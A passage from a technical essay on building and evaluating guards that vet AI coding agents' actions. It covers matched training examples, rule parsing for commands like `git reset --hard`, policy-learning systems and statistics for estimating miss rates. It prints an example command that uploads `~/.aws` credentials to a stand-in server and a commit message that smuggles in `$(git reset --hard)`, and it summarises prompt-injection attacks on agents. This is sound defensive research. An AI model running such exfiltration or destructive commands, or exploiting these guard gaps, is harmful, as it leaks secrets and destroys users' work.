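- Dangerous: `tar czf - -C "$HOME/.aws" . | curl -T - https://support.example.net/setup`
- Legitimate: `tar czf - -C docs . | curl -T - https://support.example.net/setup`

The dangerous command uploads the whole folder, including the credentials file, without using the word "credentials". The legitimate one uploads the project's public documentation in the same way. Across the four examples, the word "credentials" and the program `tar` each appear in one dangerous command and one legitimate command, so neither predicts the label on its own. The program `stat` appears only in a legitimate command, so the guard could still learn to allow any command that contains it, unless the developers add a dangerous example that uses `stat`. A real training set would need many such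 groups, with different programs, files and destinations.

Every near miss can supply half of a pair. If the guard blocked a legitimate command, developers write a dangerous counterpart, and if it missed a dangerous command, they write a legitimate one. They can check the labels by running each command in a sandbox with fake credentials and recording what it sends. SESG and HaloGuard have no equivalent check, because nobody can run a chat prompt to find out whether its purpose is harmful.

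The difference between the two halves must be visible in the guard's input. A guard that reads only the command, for instance, would learn nothing useful from two copies of `make clean` with opposite labels. Its developers would first have to give it the Makefile or a report of the command's effects.

HaloGuard's developers keep a harmful example, its harmless counterpart and all their variations together in either the training data or the test data. If the dangerous `tar` command were used for training and its legitimate counterpart for testing, the test result would partly measure whether the guard remembered the command.

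After retraining, the developers need to set the threshold again, because the new scores may be on a different scale. Keeping the old threshold could change both error rates for reasons unrelated to what the guard learned.

### A guard trained on agent actions

Matched examples have had some success with agents. *StepGuard* (Zheng, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a guard that checks each tool call before it runs. The guard was trained on synthetic data, not recorded near misses, so the results do not show whether real near misses would have worked better.

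To create the data, a language model writes a plausible task in which one action is the first unsafe one. The system keeps everything before that action and generates two safe continuations, one in which the agent refuses the action and one in which it recognises the risk and finishes the task another way. The system also generates a separate harmless task that uses the same tools, so that the guard does not learn to treat the tools themselves as dangerous. Adding these harmless tasks raised F1 from 69.2 to 75.2 on a set of harmful and harmless tool calls. This gain is more direct evidence for near-boundary data than HaloGuard's overall scores, because the comparison kept the starting model and the number of examples the same.

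StepGuard was too strict after its initial training, so Zheng and colleagues tried several ways to correct it. Their method, Balance-GRPO, measures the guard's accuracy on safe and unsafe actions during training and gives more weight to the kind it judges less accurately. Like SESG's rebalancing, it responds to whether the guard leans toward false alarms or misses, but it keeps all the examples and changes their weights. The error rates below follow from the accuracies they report.

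| Training method | FPR | FNR |
|---|---|---|
| Initial training only | 30.7% | 8.9% |
| Ordinary GRPO | 24.7% | 11.7% |
| More safe examples (70% of the data) | 15.5% | 23.8% |
| GRPO with fixed extra weight on safe actions | 14.6% | 22.5% |
| Balance-GRPO | 21.6% | 13.6% |

Each correction reduced false positives and increased misses. Balance-GRPO had the highest overall accuracy, and it and fixed weights had the two smallest gaps between the error rates. But a small gap is not the right goal if most actions are safe. If 20 in 10,000 actions were dangerous and a miss were 200 times as bad as a false block, fixed weights would be the better choice at these error rates, with total harm equal to about 2,360 false blocks, compared with 2,700 for Balance-GRPO. Balance-GRPO would be better if a miss were more than about 390 times as bad. Its target gap is also adjustable, so a team could set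 it according to how harmful misses and false blocks are in its own work.

An FPR of 21.6% would make a coding agent almost unusable, but these tests contain many risky situations, and everyday actions should be easier to judge. Zheng and colleagues therefore also ran the guard alongside a working agent on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, two tests in which attackers hide instructions in material the agent reads. StepGuard reduced the average success rate of attacks by 77.3%, while the agent's performance on harmless tasks fell by 2.8 percentage points. Training the guard with Balance-GRPO instead of ordinary GRPO raised the share of harmless tasks the agent completed by 5.4 points on AgentDojo, to 90.7%, and by 6.7 points on AgentDyn, to 66.7%. The success rate of attacks rose by only 0.3 points on each test.

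StepGuard did less well on AgentHarm, which measures whether agents carry out malicious requests. The score for malicious behaviour fell from 22.8 to 3.4, but the share of harmless tasks the agent completed also fell, from 70.9% to 52.8%. None of the other guards compared achieved a clearly good balance on this test either.

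## Revising rules and prompts without retraining

Many guards consist of rules or written instructions to a language model, so developers revise them by editing the text instead of retraining. An edit takes effect at once, colleagues can read it, and it is easy to undo. But an edit made because of one case also changes decisions on cases nobody was thinking about.

### One rule that failed in both directions

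*Lessons Outlive Their Failures* (Hassanzadeh Aliabadi, 2026) describes six weeks of using coding agents in one repository, a personal collection of documents and small Python scripts. Before each shell command ran, a script called `guard.py` checked the command's text against a list of forbidden patterns. One pattern matched `git reset --hard`, which discards uncommitted changes.

The guard blocked a harmless documentation edit because a commit message or search string quoted a forbidden command. The same false alarm happened again weeks later. The guard also missed `git -C <path> reset --hard`, where `-C` sets the folder Git works in, because its pattern required `reset` to come directly after `git`.

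In 74 recorded sessions, the guard blocked 13 of 19 forced folder deletions (`rm -rf`) and all four attempts to overwrite shared history with a force push. These counts are not enough to calculate the rate of false alarms or misses, because Hassanzadeh Aliabadi does not report which commands were dangerous. The six deletions that the guard allowed may have been misses or harmless removals of temporary folders.

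Hassanzadeh Aliabadi also kept a ledger of 118 agent failures and their fixes. Only 6 were destructive or risky actions, while 48 were out-of-date statements in documents, 35 of them found in a single day's audit. The same kind of failure recurred after the fix in 39 cases and did not recur for at least a week in 8. For the other 71, it was too early to tell or the records gave no evidence. Of the 6 destructive or risky actions, one recurred, one did not, and the outcome of the other four is unknown, so the ledger cannot show whether rules against such actions work.

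### What parsing a command repairs

Both of the guard's mistakes come from matching text. A syntax rule can avoid them because it parses the command first. In `git -C ../site reset --hard`, the parser finds the program `git`, the option `-C` with the value `../site`, the subcommand `reset` and the option `--hard`. A rule against `reset` with `--hard` then matches, whatever options come before `reset`. The parser needs a record that `-C` takes a value, or it would mistake `../site` for the subcommand.

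The made-up commands below compare the two approaches.

| Command | Text pattern | Parsed rule | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| `git commit -m 'Ban git reset --hard'` | blocks | allows | Saves a commit |
| `git -C ../site reset --hard` | allows | blocks | Discards uncommitted changes in `../site` |
| `git commit -m "Ban $(git reset --hard)"` | blocks | depends on the parser | Runs the reset first |
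| `git restore .` | allows | allows | Discards edits the user has not staged |
| `make reset` | allows | allows | Depends on the Makefile |

The third command looks much like the first, but inside double quotes the shell runs whatever stands between `$(` and `)`. It also runs text between backquotes, which agents often put around commands when they write documentation. If a double-quoted commit message mentions a forbidden command in backquotes, the shell will run that command. A guard that ignored all quoted text would stop the recurring false alarm but let these commands through. Single quotes are not always safe either, since `bash -c 'git reset --hard'` passes the quoted text to a new shell as a command.

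Parsing can still miss the last two commands, because `git restore .` does similar damage under another name and `make reset` runs commands defined in a separate file. User-defined Git shortcuts and variables filled in at run time can also hide a command. A reset does harm only if there are uncommitted changes to lose, and parsing the command cannot detect those.

A parser lets the guard judge each command in a chain separately. This could have narrowed most of the denials Roy counted, in which the rules refused a whole chain because of one command.

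### Turning false alarms into reusable exceptions

If developers write an exception for every false alarm, the list grows quickly and some exceptions will be too broad. An exception is safer if it records why the alarm was false, so the guard can check whether the same reason applies to the next case.

In *Memoir*, Guan, Hou and colleagues (2026) built a system of this kind for security scanners, which search source code for weaknesses before release. A language model reads old false alarms and writes down why each was false. Software groups alarms with similar reasons, and the language model summarises each group as one memory entry with six parts. The table gives illustrative wording for each part, using one of the paper's code examples and the blocked commit message.

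| Part of the entry | Scanner alert about a file path | Guard's block of a commit message |
|---|---|---|
| Category | User input may choose a file | Forbidden command in a text argument |
| Condition that must hold | The user can reach only files on a fixed list | The shell never runs the quoted text |
| What removes the danger | The program maps each request to a fixed file name | Single quotes around the value of `-m` |
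| Search keys | File access, fixed mapping | `git commit`, `-m`, forbidden command |
| How to verify | Check that every branch returns a constant | Parse the command and check that Git only stores the text |
| Examples | Earlier alerts with the same cause | The two blocked edits |

When the scanner raises a new alert, Memoir retrieves the five most relevant entries. It checks that each entry belongs to the alert's category and that its safety condition holds in the new code. A language model then decides whether the alert is false, using only the entries that passed both checks. Confirmed false alarms add new examples to an entry, and entries that prove unhelpful gradually lose weight.

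With GPT-4o as its language model, Memoir recognised every false alarm in the test set but also dismissed three of the six real vulnerabilities. The reported rates imply about 127 false alarms, so Memoir removed about 42 for every real vulnerability it dismissed. This is worthwhile only if missing a vulnerability does less harm than having to read 42 false alarms.

Guan and colleagues emphasise an F1 score of 98.8% for identifying false alarms. Because about 95% of the alerts were false, a filter that dismissed every alert would have scored about 97.7%.

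The paper uses two comparisons to argue that verification helps, but neither is reliable. In the first, removing verification lowers the share of dismissals that were correct from 97.7% to 92.4%. The lower figure cannot be right, because the test set has only six real vulnerabilities, and dismissing all six would have left the share at about 95%. The second compares ways of updating the memory. The system dismissed all six vulnerabilities with unverified updates, and three with either verified updates or no updates. These figures may not be measurements, because Guan and colleagues call them an "illustrative scenario" in the accompanying text and discuss what would follow if the actual results were similar.

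Memoir also cut false alarms at Tencent, from 30 to 6 for one scanner and from 149 to 8 for another. The share of alerts that were real rose from 42% to 68% for the first scanner and from 65% to 85% for the second. If these percentages describe the same alerts before and after filtering, the number of real alerts fell from about 22 to 13 for the first and from about 277 to 45 for the second. Guan and colleagues acknowledge that their figures do not show whether the system kept all the real vulnerabilities. False alarms about database queries disappeared, but those about command injection, the type of weakness closest to a guard's work, fell only from 16 to 13.

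Memoir resembles the second stage of a cascade, because it can dismiss alerts but cannot find anything the scanner missed. Google's Tricorder, a 2015 code-analysis system that Guan and colleagues cite among those refined with developers' feedback, has a similar limit. That feedback does not cover misses, so a team that judged an analyser only by complaints would rate one that never issued a warning as the best.

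### From a few reports to a general policy

A report about a single command can also lead to a general policy that covers both errors. *LiSA* (Kim, Miculicich and colleagues, May 2026) describes a way to do this for a prompted language model without changing the model. Users report wrong decisions each day, and overnight a stronger model writes up to three general policies from the reports. Each policy recommends allowing or refusing a kind of action. For example, one permits people in confidential roles to share public information, such as conference dates.

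A general policy can be too broad, so software looks for groups of similar cases with conflicting labels and writes narrower local rules for them. These rules list the differences between the acceptable and unacceptable cases. For example, telling others that a friend had attended a public lecture was usually acceptable, but not if the event belonged to a radical fringe group.

LiSA counts the supporting and contradicting reports for each general policy. It shows a policy to the guard only when the counts imply a 95% probability that the policy is right at least 55% of the time. Five supporting reports with no contradictions are enough. Local rules have no such requirement, because their purpose is to indicate that similar cases have had different outcomes. The guard's model then selects which policies and rules apply to the current action.

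Kim and colleagues simulated up to ten days of use on two tests about sharing private information and one about harmful agent tasks. They measured performance with macro-F1, the average of the F1 scores for allowing and for refusing. In some runs, they reversed 20% of the reported labels at random.

| Version of the guard | All reports correct | 20% of labels reversed |
|---|---|---|
| No adaptation | 0.818 | 0.818 |
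| General policies only | 0.936 | 0.857 |
| LiSA without the evidence requirement | 0.959 | 0.854 |
| LiSA | 0.962 | 0.917 |

The evidence requirement made little difference when the reports were correct but prevented much of the damage when some were wrong. However, random errors partly cancel out, so they are easier to withstand than the errors of tired users who approve everything, which all go in the same direction.

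In the simulation, the guard received a correction for every mistake it made that day, including every dangerous action it allowed. Real users report few misses, and LiSA's way of counting would make this problem worse. When the system writes a policy, it starts the counts of supporting and contradicting reports from all of that day's reports, even those unrelated to the policy. Suppose users report all 100 false positives and both misses from the example day. A new policy to allow something would start with 100 supporting reports and 2 contradictions, so the guard would use it immediately, even if only three complaints were related to it. A policy to block something, learned from the two misses, would start with 2 supporting reports and 100 contradictions and stay hidden. A local rule might still warn the model, but only if the log contained similar commands with the opposite label.

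A team that adopts this method for code should count only the reports that a policy covers. That is hard to do reliably when the policy is a sentence that a model has to interpret.

### Rules that software can check for conflicts

*VEPA* (Nguyen, Miculicich and colleagues, October 2026) avoids this problem by turning policies into formal rules. A language model first converts each action into a record with eight fields, including the type of action, the data involved, the recipient and the user's authorisation. Each field takes its value from a fixed list. A rule might refuse any action in which the data is confidential and the recipient is outside the organisation. Software can then find exactly which past cases a rule covers and count how often it would have been right.

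This suits guards on code because a rule can describe an effect instead of a command. If the model recorded both `git reset --hard` and `git restore .` as "discards uncommitted work", one rule would cover both variants. But the rule depends on the model recording the effect correctly. If `make reset` discards uncommitted work and the model records it as an ordinary build, the rule won't apply.

After each batch of labelled cases, a language model proposes changes to the rules. It can add, delete or rewrite a rule, split one that is too broad, or merge two that overlap. Software then checks whether any possible action would match two rules with opposite decisions. Suppose one rule forbids discarding work without authorisation and another allows discarding work in a temporary copy. An unauthorised reset in a temporary copy would match both, so VEPA would reject the change and give the language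 model this example for its next attempt. The model might then exclude temporary copies from the first rule.

VEPA treats regressions less strictly than conflicts. It gives each proposed set of rules one score for correcting recent mistakes and another for preserving decisions that used to be right, then ranks the sets by the lower of their two scores and chooses the highest. A set with scores of 0.90 for correction and 0.85 for preservation would beat one with 0.80 and 1.00, even though the second preserves every decision that used to be right. Developers of a code guard may prefer to reject any change that allows a known dangerous action again.

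Nguyen and colleagues tested VEPA on three sets of recorded agent actions, about half of them unsafe. On a mixture of all three, VEPA reached a macro-F1 of 0.86, compared with 0.80 for LiSA. Its updates turned 3.8% of previously correct decisions into mistakes, compared with 8.5% for LiSA. When the researchers removed the software checks on proposed rules, F1 fell by 0.13, more than when they removed any other part.

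The F1 comparison covers only actions to which VEPA's rules applied. These made up about 80% to 89% of the total by the end of the tests on the separate sets. This may favour VEPA, since its rules could leave the hardest cases undecided. In another test, a language model decided the remaining cases, and the combined system still did better than the alternatives.

Like F1, macro-F1 does not show which of the two errors improved. On evenly split data, a score of 0.86 could mean an FPR of 5% and an FNR of 23%, or the reverse. A team that considers a miss 200 times as bad as a false block would judge these two guards very differently. The regression rate is also hard to apply to code. If an update broke 3.8% of decisions on the example day, it would create about 380 new errors, but decisions on everyday commands should be more stable than those on test cases chosen for their risk.

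### How much evidence a new rule needs

VEPA also keeps a new rule inactive until enough labelled cases support it. Its standard is stricter than LiSA's.

| Contradicting cases | Supporting cases needed in LiSA | Supporting cases needed in VEPA |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 5 | 13 |
| 1 | about 7 | about 32 |
| 2 | about 9 | about 51 |

VEPA's limit is a median estimated error rate of 5%. The system starts by treating every error rate from 0% to 100% as equally likely. After *s* supporting cases and no contradictions, the probability that the true error rate exceeds *q* is (1 − *q*)^(*s* + 1). With 13 cases and *q* = 5%, this is 0.95^14, or about 49%. The rule is therefore only slightly more likely than not to have a true error rate below 5%, and it has a one in 20 chance of being wrong more than 19% of the time. To be 95% sure of an error rate below 5%, a team would need 58 supporting cases and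 no contradictions.

The right limit also depends on what the rule does. If a miss is 200 times as bad as a false block, a rule that allows actions should be wrong less than 0.5% of the time. By the same formula, it takes 138 uncontradicted cases to make an error rate that low more likely than not, and about 600 to be 95% sure of it. A rule that blocks actions needs far less evidence, because at that ratio even a block that is usually mistaken can be worthwhile. Both systems let developers set separate limits for the two kinds of rule. However, Nguyen and colleagues used the same limit for both kinds, and Kim and colleagues do not claim to have shown that separate limits work.

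Supporting cases can also be misleading when danger is rare. Suppose one in 100 uploads to a shared storage service leaks a secret. A rule that allowed them all would be wrong only 1% of the time, so it would pass VEPA's 5% limit. The tests could hardly reveal this problem, because about half of their actions were unsafe. One way to avoid this mistake is to look for the most dangerous action a new rule would allow, as well as counting the ordinary ones.

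VEPA usually tests a new rule on the same cases that led the language model to propose it, which makes the evidence look stronger than it is. Nguyen and colleagues suggest counting only cases that arrive afterwards, which takes longer. For a rule against a destructive command, waiting for 13 examples could be too cautious. Developers can instead write variants of the command, run them in a sandbox, and label each one by its effects.

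### Changing a prompt

Software cannot check exactly which cases an instruction in a guard's prompt covers. Suppose a guard lets an agent upload source code to a stranger's server, and a developer then adds "Treat transfers to unlisted destinations as leaks" to the prompt. The guard may now block ordinary pushes to the user's own private repository if that repository is not on the list. Two instructions can also contradict each other unnoticed until the model processes a case that both cover.

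The new instruction may have no effect. In Hassanzadeh Aliabadi's repository, a written rule told agents not to exaggerate how long a task would take to run. An older model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, gave an estimate at least twice the actual time in two of three runs without the rule and in two of three runs with it. When a model wrote a forbidden dash in a cover letter or left a wrong count in a document, however, an automatic check rejected the work and the agent corrected it. These instructions were for agents rather than guards, and the samples are tiny, but the results suggest moving an instruction into code whenever software can test the condition.

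*SafeCoEvo* (Cheng, Hu and colleagues, 2026) provides larger-scale evidence that revised text can help. Its system equips an agent with a safety prompt, a memory of past cases, written procedures for handling risks, a permission policy and a policy for acting on the guard's judgments. After each task, the system revises these and removes details such as task names so that the lessons apply to later tasks. The table gives the results over 1,024 tasks.

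| Version | Unsafe outcomes | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Text and guard both fixed | 28.4% | 43.8% |
| Text revised, guard fixed | 18.0% | 75.2% |
| Text revised, guard also retrained | 14.0% | 76.1% |

Revising the text reduced unsafe outcomes by about 10 percentage points and raised the completion rate by 31. Retraining the guard halfway through improved these measures by a further 4 points and 1 point, respectively. The guard does not account for all of the improvement from revising the text, because much of the revised text guides the agent directly, and an agent that chooses safer actions leaves the guard less to block.

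The test conditions also helped. After every task, the system learned from the benchmark whether the outcome was safe, which developers rarely know in live use. About 60% of the tasks came from only six scenarios, so later tasks had much in common with earlier ones. Cheng and colleagues say safety text can become repetitive and contradictory as it grows, which is one reason they also retrain the guard.

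Developers can change a prompt more safely by attaching the new instruction only to the cases it concerns, as LiSA does by retrieving a few relevant policies for each decision. When a change has to apply everywhere, they can keep the old prompt ready and run stored cases through both versions several times, including cases that seem unrelated to the change.

### When to retire a rule

Rules accumulate because people add one after each failure and seldom have a reason to delete any. In Hassanzadeh Aliabadi's repository, the rules grew from 4,921 to 15,122 words in 41 days, despite a clean-up that removed about a third of the text. Old fixes can also cause new problems. For example, a timer that stopped agents from editing outdated files sometimes created file conflicts while they were working.

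A rule may no longer be needed if newer models avoid the mistake that led to it. To check for this, Hassanzadeh Aliabadi recreated five past failures in copies of the repository, with and without the fix, and ran Claude Sonnet 5.5 three times on each version.

| Past failure | Fix | Failures without the fix | Failures with the fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Left wrong counts in documents | Automatic check | 3 of 3 | 0 of 2 |
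| Quoted an outdated decision | Written rule | 0 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| Used a forbidden dash | Automatic check | 0 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| Ran `git reset --hard` and lost notes | Guard on commands | 0 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| Overestimated running time | Written rule | Agent declined | Agent declined |

Only the first failure recurred without its fix. In all six runs of the destructive reset case, the model inspected the uncommitted changes and saved them to a separate file. It never attempted the reset, so the guard had nothing to block and the test does not show whether it is still needed. Even if the model attempted a destructive reset 39% of the time in this situation, there would be about a 5% chance of seeing none in six runs.

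The 30 runs took ten minutes and cost about $3.55. At that price, 299 runs of one scenario would cost about $35, and if none failed, the team could be 95% confident that the failure rate in that scenario was below 1%. Those runs would still test only one way of reaching the mistake. The original failures also involved other models, and the recreated requests may have left out whatever triggered them.

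The fifth row shows that a faithful replay has to reproduce the date as well as the files. The agent took the date from the computer's clock, so deadlines in the old files looked urgent, and a rule about focusing on deadlines made it decline the task.

Removing a rule that blocks commands allows everything that only this rule would have stopped, so removal needs as much evidence as adding a rule that allows actions. If a miss is 200 times as bad as a false block, a rule is worth keeping as long as more than one in 200 of its blocks is correct. By the earlier formula, a rule with no correct blocks would need 138 false alarms before it was more likely than not to fall short of that rate. After ten false alarms, narrowing the rule, for example by parsing the command, makes more sense than removing it.

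If a rule never blocks anything, either agents have stopped attempting the action or they now write it in a form the rule misses. The pattern for `git reset --hard` would have missed the command every time an agent wrote it with `git -C`. Developers can find out which explanation is right by testing the guard on known variants and searching the records of allowed actions for any that had the same effect.

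Models can also differ in whether they need a rule. In another set of replays, the older Claude Sonnet 5 wrote the forbidden dash once, and the automatic check caught it, whereas Sonnet 5.5 never wrote one. A team whose agents use several models should keep a rule until none of those models needs it. Hassanzadeh Aliabadi recommends recording which model version made each rule necessary and setting a date to retest the rule. If a rule guards against a mistake that is easy to undo, the team could first spend a month logging the actions the rule would have blocked, and then judge them.

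## Estimating both error rates from live traffic

After developers retrain a guard or edit its rules, they need to know how often it makes mistakes in live use. They can estimate the false-positive rate by reviewing blocked actions, because every false positive is among them. The misses are among the allowed actions, which are far more numerous and unlabelled.

Suppose a guard checks 100,000 actions in a month and blocks 1,000 of them. Reviewers examine all 1,000 and find that 180 were dangerous and 820 legitimate, so the guard's precision is 18%. To get the FPR, the team divides 820 by the total number of legitimate actions. The team doesn't know that total exactly, because some allowed actions may have been dangerous, but the uncertainty barely changes the FPR, which is 0.82% if the guard missed nothing and 0.83% if it missed 1,000 dangerous actions.

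The FNR, however, would be 0% in the first case and 85% in the second. The reviewed blocks fit both cases equally well, so reviewing them more carefully would not show which case is true.

### Verification bias

Medical researchers have the same problem when they check the diagnosis mainly in patients whose screening test was abnormal. They call the resulting error *verification bias*. *Statistical methods to correct for verification bias in diagnostic studies are inadequate* (Cronin and Vickers, 2008) illustrates it with an invented study in which 500 people are scanned for cancer. Doctors biopsy 75 of the 100 people with abnormal scans and find cancer in 50, but they biopsy only 40 of the 400 people with normal scans and find cancer in 5.

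Among the people who had a biopsy, the scan caught 50 of 55 cancers, or 91%. But the 40 biopsies after normal scans represent 400 people, so the 5 cancers they found represent about 50. Similarly, the 50 cancers found after abnormal scans represent about 67. The scan therefore caught about 67 of 117 cancers, or 57%, which makes its FNR 43% rather than 9%. The bias also inflates the FPR, from a corrected 9% to an apparent 42%.

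This correction, which Begg and Greenes developed, works only if the biopsied people with normal scans resemble the others with normal scans. A near-miss log fails that condition because it contains the allowed actions that looked most doubtful. Suppose the team's log holds 2,000 allowed near misses, and a full review finds that 40 were dangerous. Applying that 2% rate to all 99,000 allowed actions would give 1,980 misses and an FNR of 92%. Ignoring the unreviewed actions gives an FNR of 18% and an FPR of 29%, which is about 36 times the true FPR.

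Precision is less vulnerable because, as de Groot, Bossuyt and colleagues (2011) explain in *Verification problems in diagnostic accuracy studies*, it stays unbiased if the decision to check a case depends only on the test's result. A team that reviews a random tenth of all blocks can therefore estimate precision well. If it reviews only the blocks that users complained about, it will probably underestimate precision, because users are more likely to complain about false positives.

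Checking blocked and allowed actions by different methods causes another bias. de Groot and colleagues describe a study of a test for elbow fractures in which patients with a positive result were supposed to get an X-ray, while most of those with a negative result only got a follow-up phone call. When the researchers recalculated the results from the patients with a negative result who did get an X-ray, the test no longer reached the 97% reliability doctors wanted for ruling out a fracture. A team would make a similar mistake if it ran blocked commands in a sandbox but counted an allowed command as safe whenever nobody reported damage.

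### A floor from the near misses and a ceiling from a random sample

To learn about the other 97,000 allowed actions, the team reviews 2,000 of them at random and finds nothing dangerous. It now has the following data:

| Group | Actions | Reviewed | Dangerous actions found |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocked | 1,000 | 1,000 | 180 |
| Allowed near misses | 2,000 | 2,000 | 40 |
| Other allowed actions | 97,000 | 2,000 | 0 |

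Given the 40 known misses, the FNR is at least 40 / (180 + 40), or about 18%. The random sample shows how many more misses there could plausibly be.

If a share *r* of the 97,000 actions is dangerous, the chance that *n* random draws include none of them is (1 − *r*)^*n*. This chance falls to 5% when *r* is about 3/*n*, so after *n* draws without a dangerous action, the team can be 95% confident that *r* is no higher than about 3/*n*. Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues (1995), in *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred*, recommend this "rule of three" to surgeons who report operations without complications. In the published series they examined, no major blood-vessel injury led to death or the loss of a limb, but they calculated that the true risk could still have been as high as 4 in 1,000 in the largest series and 12 in 100 in the smallest.

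For the guard, 3/2,000 is 0.15%, which allows for up to about 145 misses among the 97,000 actions. The ceiling for the FNR is therefore

(40 + 145) / (180 + 40 + 145) ≈ 51%.

The FNR lies between 18% and about 51%, and the FPR is 0.82% at both ends of that range. The lower bound comes from the near-miss log and the upper bound from the random sample. The team cannot reduce the upper bound without also sampling the other allowed actions, however much time it spends on near misses.

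The floor also depends on how many near misses the team reviews. If the team reviewed only half of them and found 20 dangerous actions, the floor would drop to 10% even though the guard hadn't changed. A lower floor is therefore a sign of a better guard only if the team searched equally hard both times.

The ceiling is not an estimate of the FNR either, because the true number of further misses could be zero. *Exploring the scientific underpinnings of investigating safety signals* notes a similar problem in drug safety, where regulators use the rule of three for side effects that no trial participant had. The rule can make such a side effect look more common than it is. Regulators still prefer it to rates based on voluntary reports from doctors and patients, which are the medical equivalent of a complaint log.

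Each action in the random sample stands for 48.5 actions, so finding one dangerous action among the 2,000 would raise the estimated FNR from 18% to 33%. Cronin and Vickers found the same sensitivity to a single case in their example, where finding one cancer instead of two after a normal scan raised the estimated share of cancers caught from 77% to 87%.

Labelling mistakes matter just as much. If reviewers wrongly labelled one in 1,000 legitimate actions as dangerous, they would record about two false misses in the sample, which the team would count as 97 when scaling up. A second reviewer should check every dangerous label from the random sample and some of the harmless ones.

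The rule of three also assumes the draws are independent. For Anthropic's August post, the testing company Trajectory Labs ran 72 attacks ten times each against agents in auto mode. The attacks hid instructions in material the agent would read, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded. If the attempts were independent, the upper bound on the success rate would be about 0.4%. But an attack that fails once will often fail again, and if all ten runs of each attack always had the same result, the upper bound would be 3/72, or about 4%. Similarly, 2,000 actions from 20 long coding sessions provide much less evidence about a guard than 2,000 actions from 2,000 sessions.

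The attack test also measured the agent and its guard together. Even without auto mode, only 0.09% of the attacks on average succeeded against Anthropic's latest models, so the guard had little left to block.

### Sampling risky actions more heavily

To lower the ceiling from 51% to 25% with a plain random sample, the team would have to review about 14,500 of the 97,000 actions and find nothing dangerous.

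Marchant and Rubinstein (2020), in *Needle in a Haystack*, give a general formula for the cost of estimating recall from a random sample of all traffic. The number of labels needed is

recall × (1 − recall) / (base rate × *w*²),

where *w* is the standard error the team is willing to accept. With a recall of 82%, a base rate of 0.22% and a standard error of five percentage points, this comes to about 27,000 labels. If dangerous actions were half as common, the team would need twice as many.

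A team can do better by sampling more heavily where it expects misses and correcting for this with weights. It must record each action's probability of selection, π. A dangerous action that had a one in ten chance of selection then counts as ten. In general,

estimated misses = Σ 1/πᵢ

estimated FNR = estimated misses / (estimated misses + dangerous blocks),

where the sum covers all the dangerous allowed actions that reviewers found. Every allowed action needs some chance of selection, or the estimate will leave out any misses in the excluded group.

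Suppose 10,000 of the 97,000 actions delete files, change shared systems or send data outside, and the other 87,000 appear to do none of these things. The team reviews 1,000 from each group. Each dangerous action found in the risky group counts as 10, and each one found in the other group counts as 87. Each of the 40 known misses counts as 1 because the team reviewed all the near misses. If reviewers find four dangerous actions in the risky group and none in the other, the estimate is 40 + 4 × 10 = 80 misses, and the estimated FNR is 80/260, or about 31%.

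Suppose 50 misses remain, 45 of them in the risky group, which makes the true FNR 33%. The estimated number of remaining misses has a standard error of about 49 with 2,000 plain random draws, and about 29 with weighted sampling that takes 1,000 draws from each group. One standard error either side of the truth corresponds to an FNR of 19% to 44% with plain sampling and 25% to 40% with weighted sampling. The team would need about 5,500 plain random draws to match the precision of the weighted sample.

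The gain depends on guessing correctly where the misses are. If the team finds no misses in the 2,000 weighted draws, all the remaining misses could still be among the 87,000 actions it sampled thinly. By the rule of three, there could be up to 261 misses there, and the upper bound on the FNR would rise to 63%.

Weighted sampling lowers the ceiling only if the team can assume something about the thinly sampled group, for instance that actions there are at most a tenth as likely to be dangerous as those in the risky group. If *r* is the dangerous share of the risky group, the highest value that fits finding no dangerous actions in either sample comes from 1,000*r* + 1,000*r*/10 = 3, which gives *r* = 0.27%. The two groups together could then hold about 51 further misses, and the ceiling drops from 51% to 34%. The team can test the assumption by continuing to sample the thinly sampled group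 every month.

Experiments on other classifiers show similar gains and limits. Marsigli and Lopez de Haro (2026), in *Label-Efficient Monitoring of Classification Models via Stratified Importance Sampling*, divided cases into groups and, within each group, sampled more heavily where a score suggested a mistake. They estimated the overall error rate, not the FNR. On handwritten digits, where the classifier erred 1% of the time, their method's mean squared error with 100 labels was about a ninth of random sampling's. On loan defaults, where errors were far more common, it was about 70% of random sampling's with 500 labels. On a breast cancer data set, sampling by a poorly suited score without the groups did no better than random sampling.

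*An AI-powered Tool for Central Bank Business Liaisons* (2025) reports an experiment on estimating recall for software that finds the few paragraphs about wages in a large collection of text. Drawing 60 paragraphs from each of ten groups and weighting them reduced the spread of the recall estimate from 0.034 to 0.014. Neither experiment involved a guard on code. If such a guard gave a harmful Makefile a low score, the sample would also be less likely to include that file.

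### How precise a measured miss rate is

Anthropic measured auto mode's 17% FNR on only 52 real overeager actions. It did not publish the number of misses, but 9 of 52 is the closest whole number. (The 6.6% it gave for stage 1 alone matches no whole number out of 52, so the rates may be averages over several runs.)

A confidence interval shows how far such a rate could be from the true one by chance. For small samples, Brown, Cai and DasGupta (2001), in *Interval Estimation for a Binomial Proportion*, recommend the Wilson interval or a similar one called the Jeffreys interval. NIST's *Confidence intervals* gives the Wilson formula, in which *p* is the measured rate, *n* the number of cases and *z* is 1.96 for 95% confidence:

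[*p* + *z*²/2*n* ± *z*√(*p*(1 − *p*)/*n* + *z*²/4*n*²)] / (1 + *z*²/*n*).

For 9 misses in 52 cases, the interval for the miss rate runs from about 9% to 30%. Auto mode's false positive rate of 0.4% is much more certain. If the guard blocked 40 of 10,000 harmless tool calls, the interval is 0.3% to 0.5%.

The more familiar interval, *p* ± *z*√(*p*(1 − *p*)/*n*), works badly for rare errors. Its lower end can be negative, and if the sample contains no misses, its width is zero, which would mean the team was certain that the guard never misses anything. Brown and colleagues calculated that with a true rate of 0.5% and a sample of 592 cases, a nominal 95% interval of this kind contains the true rate only 79% of the time.

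The formula above assumes that every case has the same weight. For weighted samples, *A note on Wilson coverage intervals for proportions estimated from complex samples*, published by Statistics Canada, replaces *n* with an effective sample size, the number of plain random draws that would give an equally precise estimate. It can be much smaller than the number of cases reviewed if a few of them have very large weights.

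With 52 cases, a team could easily fail to notice a real improvement. Suppose a new version of the guard missed 5 of another 52 dangerous actions, or about 10%. The interval for that rate would run from 4% to 21%. Even if the two versions were equally good, a difference at least this large would occur by chance about a quarter of the time. To have an 80% chance of detecting a fall in the FNR from 17% to 8.5%, the team would need about 240 dangerous actions for each version. At a base rate of 0.2%, that many occur in about 120,000 actions, and reviewers would still have to find them. Testing both versions on the same recorded cases usually requires fewer dangerous actions, because neither version can get an easier set by chance.

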